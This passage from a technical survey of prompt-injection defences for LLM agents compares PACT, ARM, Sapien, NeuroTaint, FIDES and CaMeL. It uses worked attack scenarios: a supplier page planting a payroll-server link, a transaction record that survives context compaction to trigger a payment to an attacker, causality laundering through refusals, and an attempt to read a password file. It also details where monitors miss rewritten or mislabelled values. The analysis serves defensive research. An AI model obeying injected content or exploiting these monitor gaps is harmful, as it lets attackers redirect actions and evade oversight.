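Another test compared four levels of precision. The lowest treats all of a tool's arguments alike and requires full trust, and the second sets one threshold for each type of tool. The third adds roles, and the highest adds certification. All four blocked every attack. The share of legitimate cases allowed rose from 8.3% at the lowest level to 58.3% at the second and 100% at the third. That left no room for improvement, so the test doesn't show how useful certification is.

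### The AgentDojo runs

The tests in AgentDojo were more realistic, because PACT had to infer the roles and provenance itself. AgentDojo simulates office, Slack, travel and banking environments, with 97 ordinary tasks and 27 attack tasks. Debenedetti and colleagues normally combine the two kinds of task within each environment, which gives 629 security cases. Fan and colleagues' security figures are instead consistent with 27 attacks per model.

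| Model | Ordinary tasks completed, no defence | With CaMeL | With PACT | Attacks resisted without a defence, out of 27 | Attacks resisted with PACT, out of 27 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen-turbo | 20.6% | 11.3% | 18.6% | 25 | 26 or 27 |
| Qwen-plus | 60.8% | 29.9% | 45.4% | 24 | 26 or 27 |
| Qwen-max | 46.4% | 29.9% | 38.1% | 26 | 27 |
| Qwen2.5-72B | 46.4% | 28.9% | 42.3% | 26 | 27 |
| GPT-4o-mini | 59.8% | 30.9% | 46.4% | 24 | 27 |

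The paper's main results table gives PACT 100% security on Qwen-turbo and Qwen-plus, but the text gives 96.3% (26 of 27) for both. A later table also gives 96.3%, next to a task completion rate of 18.6%, which matches Qwen-turbo. The text reports 100% security on the three strongest models, meaning the last three in the main table, but without a defence Qwen-plus completed more ordinary tasks than any of them.

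Whichever figures are correct, PACT stopped only one to three more attacks than no defence. The undefended agents already resisted 24 to 26 of the 27 attacks (88.9% to 96.3%), which left little room for improvement. Even a defence that stops all 27 attacks could have a true success rate as low as about 88%, using a standard 95% confidence interval. Attacks that usually succeed against undefended agents would give a much better test.

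The gain over CaMeL in ordinary work is more convincing. With GPT-4o-mini, PACT completed 45 of the 97 tasks, compared with 30 for CaMeL and 58 for the agent without a defence. Choi and colleagues also found that a strict version of CaMeL prevented many ordinary tasks. PACT seems to reduce this problem, but it still completed fewer tasks than the undefended agent.

The results for FIDES are harder to explain. In Fan and colleagues' runs, agents with FIDES never stopped more attacks than agents with no defence, and on two models they stopped one fewer. Costa and colleagues had earlier tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o and a stronger type of attack. They reported 152 successful injections against a basic agent and none against an agent using FIDES with its policies. The two teams may have used different policies, but Fan and colleagues don't explain the difference.

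The evaluation also included versions of PACT that applied the same threshold to every argument. With user-level trust required, all 27 attacks were stopped, but the agent completed only 14.4% of ordinary tasks. With external values accepted, it completed 18.6%, but only 25 attacks were stopped. PACT itself also completed 18.6% and stopped 26 attacks. On this model, then, using roles allowed four more ordinary tasks than the strict threshold and stopped one more attack than the lax one, which is rather weak evidence that roles are important.

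### Inferred roles and provenance

PACT's guarantee assumes that the contracts are correct, the provenance records don't overstate trust and the certification procedures are sound. In the AgentDojo runs, the software generated 74 contracts from the tools' names, arguments and descriptions. To find a value's source, it looked first for an exact match in the user's instructions or earlier tool results, then for recognisable transformations, and used a language model for some of the remaining cases.

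On 20 real MCP tools, this process assigned the right role 87.1% of the time and the right provenance 77.4% of the time. If errors in role and provenance were independent, both assignments would be right about two-thirds of the time. PACT chooses the lower trust level when it is unsure about a sensitive argument, so many of its errors are safe but block legitimate work. An error that gives a value too much trust may admit an attack.

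The most serious example is a tool whose output receives too much trust. If the contract for the page-reading tool mistakenly labelled its results as user-level, the payroll link would pass PACT's check even if every other part worked correctly. Systematic mistakes with roles can be just as damaging. Security fell to 40% when Fan and colleagues mislabelled every target as content, but remained at 88%, with some additional policies in place, when they mislabelled half the roles at random.

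Provenance is hard to infer because a model can rewrite what it reads. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) explains that a monitor with access only to tools' inputs and outputs cannot observe how the model turned untrusted text into an argument. An exact match would identify the supplier's link if the model copied it, but might miss a URL that the model assembled from a description on the page. PACE also matches arguments to earlier values and can recognise some standard encodings, but not paraphrases, translations or secrets split into pieces.

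Fan and colleagues attribute the remaining gap between the two sets of tests mainly to errors in role and provenance labels. That can't be the whole explanation, because even with perfect labels, PACT would refuse Dora's address for the invitation because it came from a web page.

People can also check the contracts before using them. In a seven-day trial outside AgentDojo, setting up contracts for 15 tools took 75 minutes, and PACT then blocked all 13 attacks and none of the 267 legitimate calls. The trial was small, but it suggests that a company with few tools could manage the contracts.

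### PACT across a hand-off

Fan and colleagues designed PACT for an agent whose software preserves the tags on its values. In the original supplier example, the planning agent sends a URL to the fetching agent. If the fetching agent's monitor treats that message as a user instruction, it gives the payroll address user-level trust and allows it through. Anthropic's `web_fetch` has much the same weakness.

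Treating the planning agent's message as a tool's output would be safer, but every URL in it would then fall below user-level trust, and the fetching agent would refuse even a URL that the employee had written. The origin record suggested for A2A messages would solve this if the monitors used it to pass on each value's tag. The URL from the supplier's page would then remain external, and the employee's URL would keep its user-level trust.

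The receiving monitor should accept tags only from software it trusts, because an outside company's agent could label its own address as coming from the employee.

### Attacks outside PACT's scope

PACT doesn't stop an attacker from influencing which tool an agent calls. A web page might lead the agent to call a tool that deletes old records, with only constants from the agent's own software as arguments. Every argument would pass PACT's checks, although the user never asked for the deletion.

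Harmful text can also pass through a content argument. The false price list could lead to a misleading summary, which PACT would allow the agent to email to the boss. A link to a fake login page could pass in a message body in the same way. One of the FIDES policies would block the message if the link were identified as untrusted, but it would also block harmless links from outside sources.

Fan and colleagues tested PACT on Agent-SafetyBench, which covers many kinds of unsafe behaviour besides prompt injection. It blocked 74.7% of the unsafe cases but completed only 39.3% of the harmless ones. It did best on risks such as loss of property, where it blocked 90.1%, and worst on misinformation, where it blocked 48.1%. Misinformation may be harder to block because a false statement can appear in an argument that is supposed to contain outside text.

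Like the origin labels described earlier, PACT cannot show that a page persuaded the agent to misuse an address from the user. *AgentSentry* (2026) also notes that provenance alone does not establish whether the user authorised an action. If a user asked an agent to email an order to the supplier and a payroll summary to the finance director, and a page made the agent swap the recipients, PACT would allow both emails. A rule against payroll data in emails would keep the summary from the supplier, but also from the finance director. FIDES and CaMeL record who may read each value, so a policy in either system could block the summary from going to the supplier and still allow it to go to the finance director.

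## ARM: identical last requests with different histories

PACT can treat two similar tool calls differently because it records where each argument came from. If an employee causes a request in one case and a hostile page causes the same request in another, a filter that checks only the final request must allow both or block both. ARM, a monitor from April 2026, examines the steps that led to a request, including earlier actions it blocked. Its published tests are small, and the method depends on knowing what influenced each value, which is hard to establish once a model has rewritten the value.

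### Two histories of one request

Suppose the fetching agent is logged in to the company's account on the supplier's website and is about to open the order-cancellation link:

```
GET https://supplier.example/orders/cancel?id=311
```

Two different tasks could have led to it:

| Step | The employee chose the address | The page chose the address |
|---|---|---|
| Employee's request | "Cancel order 311 with this link" | "Get the current prices" |
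| Reading agent | Has no part in the task | Returns the altered price-list link |
| Planning agent's task | "Open the cancellation link" | "Download the current price list" |
| Final request | The `GET` request above | The same `GET` request |
| Correct decision | Allow | Block |

A final-request filter's verdict depends only on the request, so identical requests get identical verdicts. The filter must either let the attacker cancel an order or stop the employee from cancelling one. Random decisions don't help, because a filter that allows the request with probability *p* wrongly allows the attacker's request with probability *p* and wrongly blocks the employee's with probability 1 − *p*. The two error rates therefore always add up to 1, and a better model inside the filter can only change *p*.

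The filter could do better if the request carried more information, such as the employee's name. It could then let payroll staff download the payroll export and refuse everyone else. But it still couldn't distinguish the two histories above if the same employee started both tasks. The altered payroll link would also work whenever someone from payroll asked for the supplier's prices.

Letting the filter read the whole conversation helps only if the text shows who wrote what. Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026), in *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, prove a limit for any check that reads text without a reliable record of its authors. Let *P*<sub>L</sub> be the probability distribution of that text when a legitimate source wrote a certain record in it, and *P*<sub>A</sub> the distribution when an attacker did. Let *p*<sub>L</sub> and *p*<sub>A</sub> be the probabilities that the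 check allows a sensitive call using the value in that record. Then:

*p*<sub>L</sub> − *p*<sub>A</sub> ≤ TV(*P*<sub>L</sub>, *P*<sub>A</sub>)

TV is the total variation distance, the largest difference between the probabilities that the two distributions give to any set of texts. It is 0 if the distributions are identical and 1 if they don't overlap. For two identical requests it is 0, which gives the argument above. The theorem also explains why injected instructions are easier to catch than false data. A legitimate price page wouldn't contain an order to an AI assistant, but a false account number can look exactly like a real one.

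### After a correct block

Now suppose the attacker uses the payroll link instead and the destination check refuses it. The link is still on the supplier's page. The reading agent may also have saved it in a shared file such as `suppliers.json`, and another agent could open that file next week with a script that has no destination check. The attacker can also replace the link with one that passes. To deal with the cause, the company would have to:

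1. find the page or record that supplied the address;
2. stop its agents from reading that source until someone has repaired it;
3. correct or delete any notes, summaries and unfinished tasks based on it;
4. check the requests that agents have already sent because of it.

The filter's log contains the address but not the page. Searching for `10.0.4.17` would find exact copies, but it would miss a note saying that the price list had moved to the payroll server. *From Agent Traces to Trust* recommends linking each source to the arguments, the outputs and whatever later uses those outputs. The company could then trace the address back to the page and find everything else the page had affected. Stored summaries often break these links, because condensing many sourced records into one summary usually loses their sources first, according to *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of agent memory.

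Summarising a conversation can even lead a defence to allow an action it had already blocked. When a long conversation approaches the limit of what a model can read, the agent's software has a model summarise the earlier part, a step called compaction. Fei and colleagues tested this with Progent, a defence that derives an agent's permissions from the user's request. In their example, a user asks a banking agent about spending in March, and a transaction record contains an instruction to pay the attacker. Progent blocks the transfer. The summary then lists the transfer as unfinished work, and the next set of permissions allows one transfer, to the attacker's account.

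This happens because the software puts the summary where Progent expects the user's message. Claude Code and Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, did so in all 1,108 automatic compactions that Fei and colleagues recorded. In another test, the user had named the right account and later asked the agent to pay the rent, but a notice gave a false one. Permissions derived from a frontier model's summary allowed the false account in 91% of cases with one policy-writing model and 59% with another, while permissions derived from the user's words never allowed it. Fei and colleagues had changed Progent to derive new permissions for each request because its usual fixed permissions let the agent finish only 12% of later tasks, compared with 68% after the change.

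The remedy is to attach a cryptographic tag to each user message when it arrives and pass the tagged messages, word for word, to the policy-writing model. The agent still reads the summary. No attack succeeded in 40 test episodes with this defence. The defence protects the permissions but leaves the attacker's text in the summary, so the company would still have to remove that text.

### How ARM uses earlier steps

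*Causality Laundering* (Chinaei, 2026) describes ARM, the Agentic Reference Monitor, which sits between an agent and its tools. ARM keeps a graph of tool calls, the data they return, the individual fields in that data, and refused calls. Links in the graph show which data went into each call and which call produced each result.

Before a call, ARM finds all the data that led to it, however many steps back, and assigns the call the lowest trust level among them. The levels, from highest to lowest, are system instructions, user input, trusted tools, untrusted tools and tool descriptions. By default, ARM refuses a call if its level is below that of trusted tools. ARM would therefore allow the cancellation if the employee supplied the link, but would refuse it if the link came from the supplier's page and that page counts as untrusted. ARM also checks whether an earlier refused call may have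 influenced the new one.

Chinaei compared ARM with a simpler baseline that checks only whether an argument's value appeared earlier in the agent's tool history. All other checks were the same. The baseline allowed the final call in all three scenarios, and ARM blocked it each time:

| Type of influence | Earlier steps | Final call |
|---|---|---|
| Through a refusal | ARM refuses to read `/etc/shadow`, a file of password data | Email saying "shadow file exists" |
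| Through several steps | The agent reads an untrusted email about a $50,000 transfer, and a formatting tool rewrites it | Email to the finance department with the rewritten text |
| Through one field | A contact record contains a trusted name and an untrusted email address | Email to the untrusted address |

In the first scenario, which Chinaei calls "causality laundering", an attacker learns something from a refusal and sends it out in a later call that looks harmless. The refused call returned no data, so a system that tracks only returned data can't trace the leak. The example doesn't quite work, because ARM refused the call based on a list of sensitive paths and would have done so whether or not the file existed. The agent therefore couldn't learn from the refusal that the file existed. An operating system's error could reveal this, because it distinguishes "permission denied" from "file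 not found".

ARM can't observe the model's reasoning, so it treats each refusal as influencing the next call. Chinaei acknowledges that this may block harmless calls and miss leaks that take more steps. More seriously, the published algorithm seems to block the rest of the session after one refusal, because it refuses the call after a refusal, records this as another refusal and links that to the following call. The prototype may avoid this by applying the rule only to certain tools, but the algorithm includes no such limit.

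The second scenario shows why a monitor needs to look further back than the last tool. However, an employee might reasonably ask an agent to summarise a supplier's email for the finance department, which involves the same sequence of calls. ARM would block that request, whereas PACT could accept outside text in the body of an email.

In the third scenario, the baseline accepts the attacker's address because it appeared in the contact record. Anthropic's rule for `web_fetch` has a similar weakness, since it accepts a URL that appeared on an earlier page. ARM blocks the email only because a developer has marked the field containing the address as untrusted. Without the label, that field gets the same trust level as the rest of the record.

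### What three scenarios can establish

The three scenarios can support Chinaei's main claim that the graph distinguishes cases the baseline can't, because one counterexample is enough to show that the baseline misses a type of attack. They don't measure how often ARM would stop real attacks or block ordinary work. Chinaei designed each scenario so that one feature of the graph would decide the result, used a deliberately minimal baseline, and reports no large-scale tests with a live model.

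The tests also leave out the difficult step of working out which data went into an argument that a model wrote. ARM's algorithm receives a list of the data behind each call, so other software has to produce that list. All the checks together took less than a millisecond per call on a laptop-class processor, in sessions with tens of tool calls. This is negligible compared with a model's response time, which is usually at least a tenth of a second, but it doesn't appear to include the time needed to trace the data.

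Chinaei studied a single agent and left hand-offs between agents for future work. If the fetching agent had its own graph that began with the planning agent's message, ARM would have no record of the supplier's page, just as the original message had none.

PACT provides a second test of tracking across several steps. In a controlled comparison, Fan and colleagues switched off the list of earlier sources that PACT keeps with each value. The share of attacks blocked fell from 100% to 80%, and all the legitimate calls still went through. The missed attacks passed web text through an intermediate tool. The drop depends on how many of the test attacks did this, so it doesn't predict how many real attacks would get through.

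### Rules about the order of calls

ARM starts from a proposed call and examines the history behind it. A policy can instead state in advance which sequences of calls a task allows. In *Sapien*, Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues (2026) describe a Google system that writes such a policy from the user's request before the agent reads any outside content. If a user asks to refund whoever sent money last week, the agent must first list the transactions. It may then send money only to a sender and in an amount that appear in last week's transactions. A policy that only listed permitted tools would allow a payment of any size to anyone.

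For the supplier task, a similar policy might be:

1. Fetch the page that the employee named.
2. Download one file whose address appears on that page and has the same host.

This uses the page as data for a fixed rule, which the page can't change even if it completely takes over the agent's model. Tiffany and colleagues tested that worst case by checking whether each policy allowed any sequence of calls that would complete an attack. The policies ruled out 93–95% of attacks on AgentDojo and 62–85% on Toolathlon, a benchmark with longer tasks, where tool allowlists stopped about half as many. Agents completed almost as many tasks as they did without restrictions.

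When Sapien refuses a call, it reports the refusal to the agent so that the agent can try something else. This avoids interrupting the user, but it also creates the kind of signal that causality laundering exploits. Tiffany and colleagues acknowledge that a hijacked agent could leak information through the order of its permitted calls.

The policy for the supplier task would still allow the cancellation link if that link appeared on the employee's chosen page, because the link has the same host as the price list. The argument about identical requests would then apply to origin labels too, since both links would come from the same page. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) describes this problem using two record numbers from one listing, and adds a rule that blocks the action if any listing the agent has read points to a different record.

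### Following a value after a model rewrites it

ARM and Sapien both need to connect an argument to earlier data. As with PACT, exact matching can miss the connection when a model summarises or translates what it has read. The supplier's page could describe the payroll server as "ten dot zero dot four dot seventeen" and leave the model to write the address in digits. *AGATE* (2026), which describes another monitor based on provenance, names rewritten parameters and legitimate reuse of text as the main difficulties for checks that compare content.

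NeuroTaint, which the ChainFuzzer comparison introduced, tries to follow meaning as well as exact text. Cai and colleagues describe four comparisons between a source and a later tool call:

1. Add a unique marker to the source's text and look for it in the call's arguments.
2. Look for copied characters, and report a match if they make up at least 15% of the shorter text.
3. Convert both texts into lists of numbers that represent their meaning, and report a match if their similarity is at least 0.60.
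4. Compare the arguments with small parts of the source, in case one hostile paragraph sits in a long, harmless page.

If none of these finds a match, NeuroTaint uses a language model to judge whether the agent would have made the same call without the source. It tests one source at a time. If two pages give the same instruction, removing either one leaves the other, so the model may correctly predict that the call would still happen. NeuroTaint would then attribute the call to neither page.

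The benchmark contained 200 cases in which a source influenced a later call:

| Evidence needed to find the influence | Cases | Found |
|---|---|---|
| Exact marker | 15 | 15 |
| Copied or nearly copied text | 45 | 45 |
| Similar meaning, including reuse in another session or by another agent | 85 | 75 |
| Fragments of a long source | 15 | 15 |
| Influence on the decision, with no text carried over | 40 | 37 |

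These results are encouraging for rewritten text, but the false alarms are more worrying than their total suggests. NeuroTaint raised false alarms in 16 of 200 harmless cases. In 14 of the 200, the source and the call were on the same topic but neither had influenced the other, and NeuroTaint flagged all 14. Such overlap is common in ordinary work. An employee's email about brake cables will resemble a supplier's page about brake cables even if the employee wrote every word. If half of all harmless cases were like this, NeuroTaint would raise false alarms in about half of all harmless cases.

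One setting may also have made the results look better. Cai and colleagues used a similarity threshold of 0.95 instead of 0.60 for what they call safe-control policies. If these were the policies for the harmless cases, the higher threshold made NeuroTaint much less likely to raise false alarms. A company couldn't choose the threshold this way because it wouldn't know in advance which cases were harmless.

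Cai and colleagues also report that FIDES missed 92 cases and raised 106 false alarms. But their version of FIDES raised no alarms on four of the 20 agent frameworks, which accounts for 40 of the misses. They may have connected it to those frameworks incorrectly.

A second model can remove some false alarms. When Claude Opus 4.6 reviewed NeuroTaint's alerts, the combined system flagged 179 of the 200 real cases and none of the harmless ones. However, the reviewer's instructions closely fit the benchmark. They listed topical overlap as a reason to clear an alert and required the model to treat the benchmark's test markers as dangerous.

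### When everything becomes untrusted

A system can avoid guessing what influenced a value by distrusting everything a model writes after reading untrusted text, as FIDES does. *Autonomous LLM Agent Worms* (2026) sets out the same rule and allows only a separate procedure, not the model, to mark the output as trusted. Paraphrasing or translating the untrusted text doesn't defeat this rule, because the rule doesn't rely on comparing texts.

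It soon blocks useful work, though. When the reading agent opens the supplier's page, its report becomes untrusted. The planning agent reads the report, so every task it writes afterwards is untrusted, including a request for an internal document that the employee named that morning. When the fetching agent reads one of those tasks, all three agents are affected after only two messages. Researchers call this gradual spread label creep. PACT likewise blocked more ordinary work when it required user-level trust for every argument.

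Starting each task with an empty context would limit the spread, but the agents would lose useful information from earlier work. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) describes another option for private data, in which ordinary software keeps a cautious list of the records an agent has read and a separate model compares them with the agent's proposed output. Because this model can read the original records, it can recognise paraphrases and coded references that a filter on the outgoing text would miss. The comparison avoids blocking every message from an agent that has read private data, but the decision again depends on a model that can make mistakes.

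### Requests that need no history

A final-request filter works well against requests that no legitimate task could produce. If the fetching agent never needs to reach internal machines, every request to a private address is wrong, whoever chose it, so the filter can refuse them all without knowing their histories or blocking legitimate work.

ARM starts with checks of this kind. Before it uses the graph, it blocks sensitive file paths, arguments that look like passwords or keys, and any text argument longer than 10,000 characters. In the refusal scenario, one of these simple checks stopped the agent from reading the password file. ARM has no equivalent check for web addresses. It only logs arguments named `url`, `endpoint` or `host`, and enforcing rules on them is left for later work.

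That omission matters most when tracking fails. If ARM finds no source data for a call, it gives the call the highest trust level, the same as system instructions. Suppose the model assembles the payroll address from words on the supplier's page, and the tracking fails to link the two. ARM would then treat the address as fully trusted. A destination check would still refuse `10.0.4.17`, because it doesn't depend on knowing where the address came from.

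The company can also redesign its tools so that fewer requests depend on their history. It could give employees a separate `cancel_order` tool that accepts only an order number. The fetching agent's filter could then refuse every address under `/orders/`, since no legitimate task would need one. The new tool would still need an origin check, as would the document-number tool suggested earlier.
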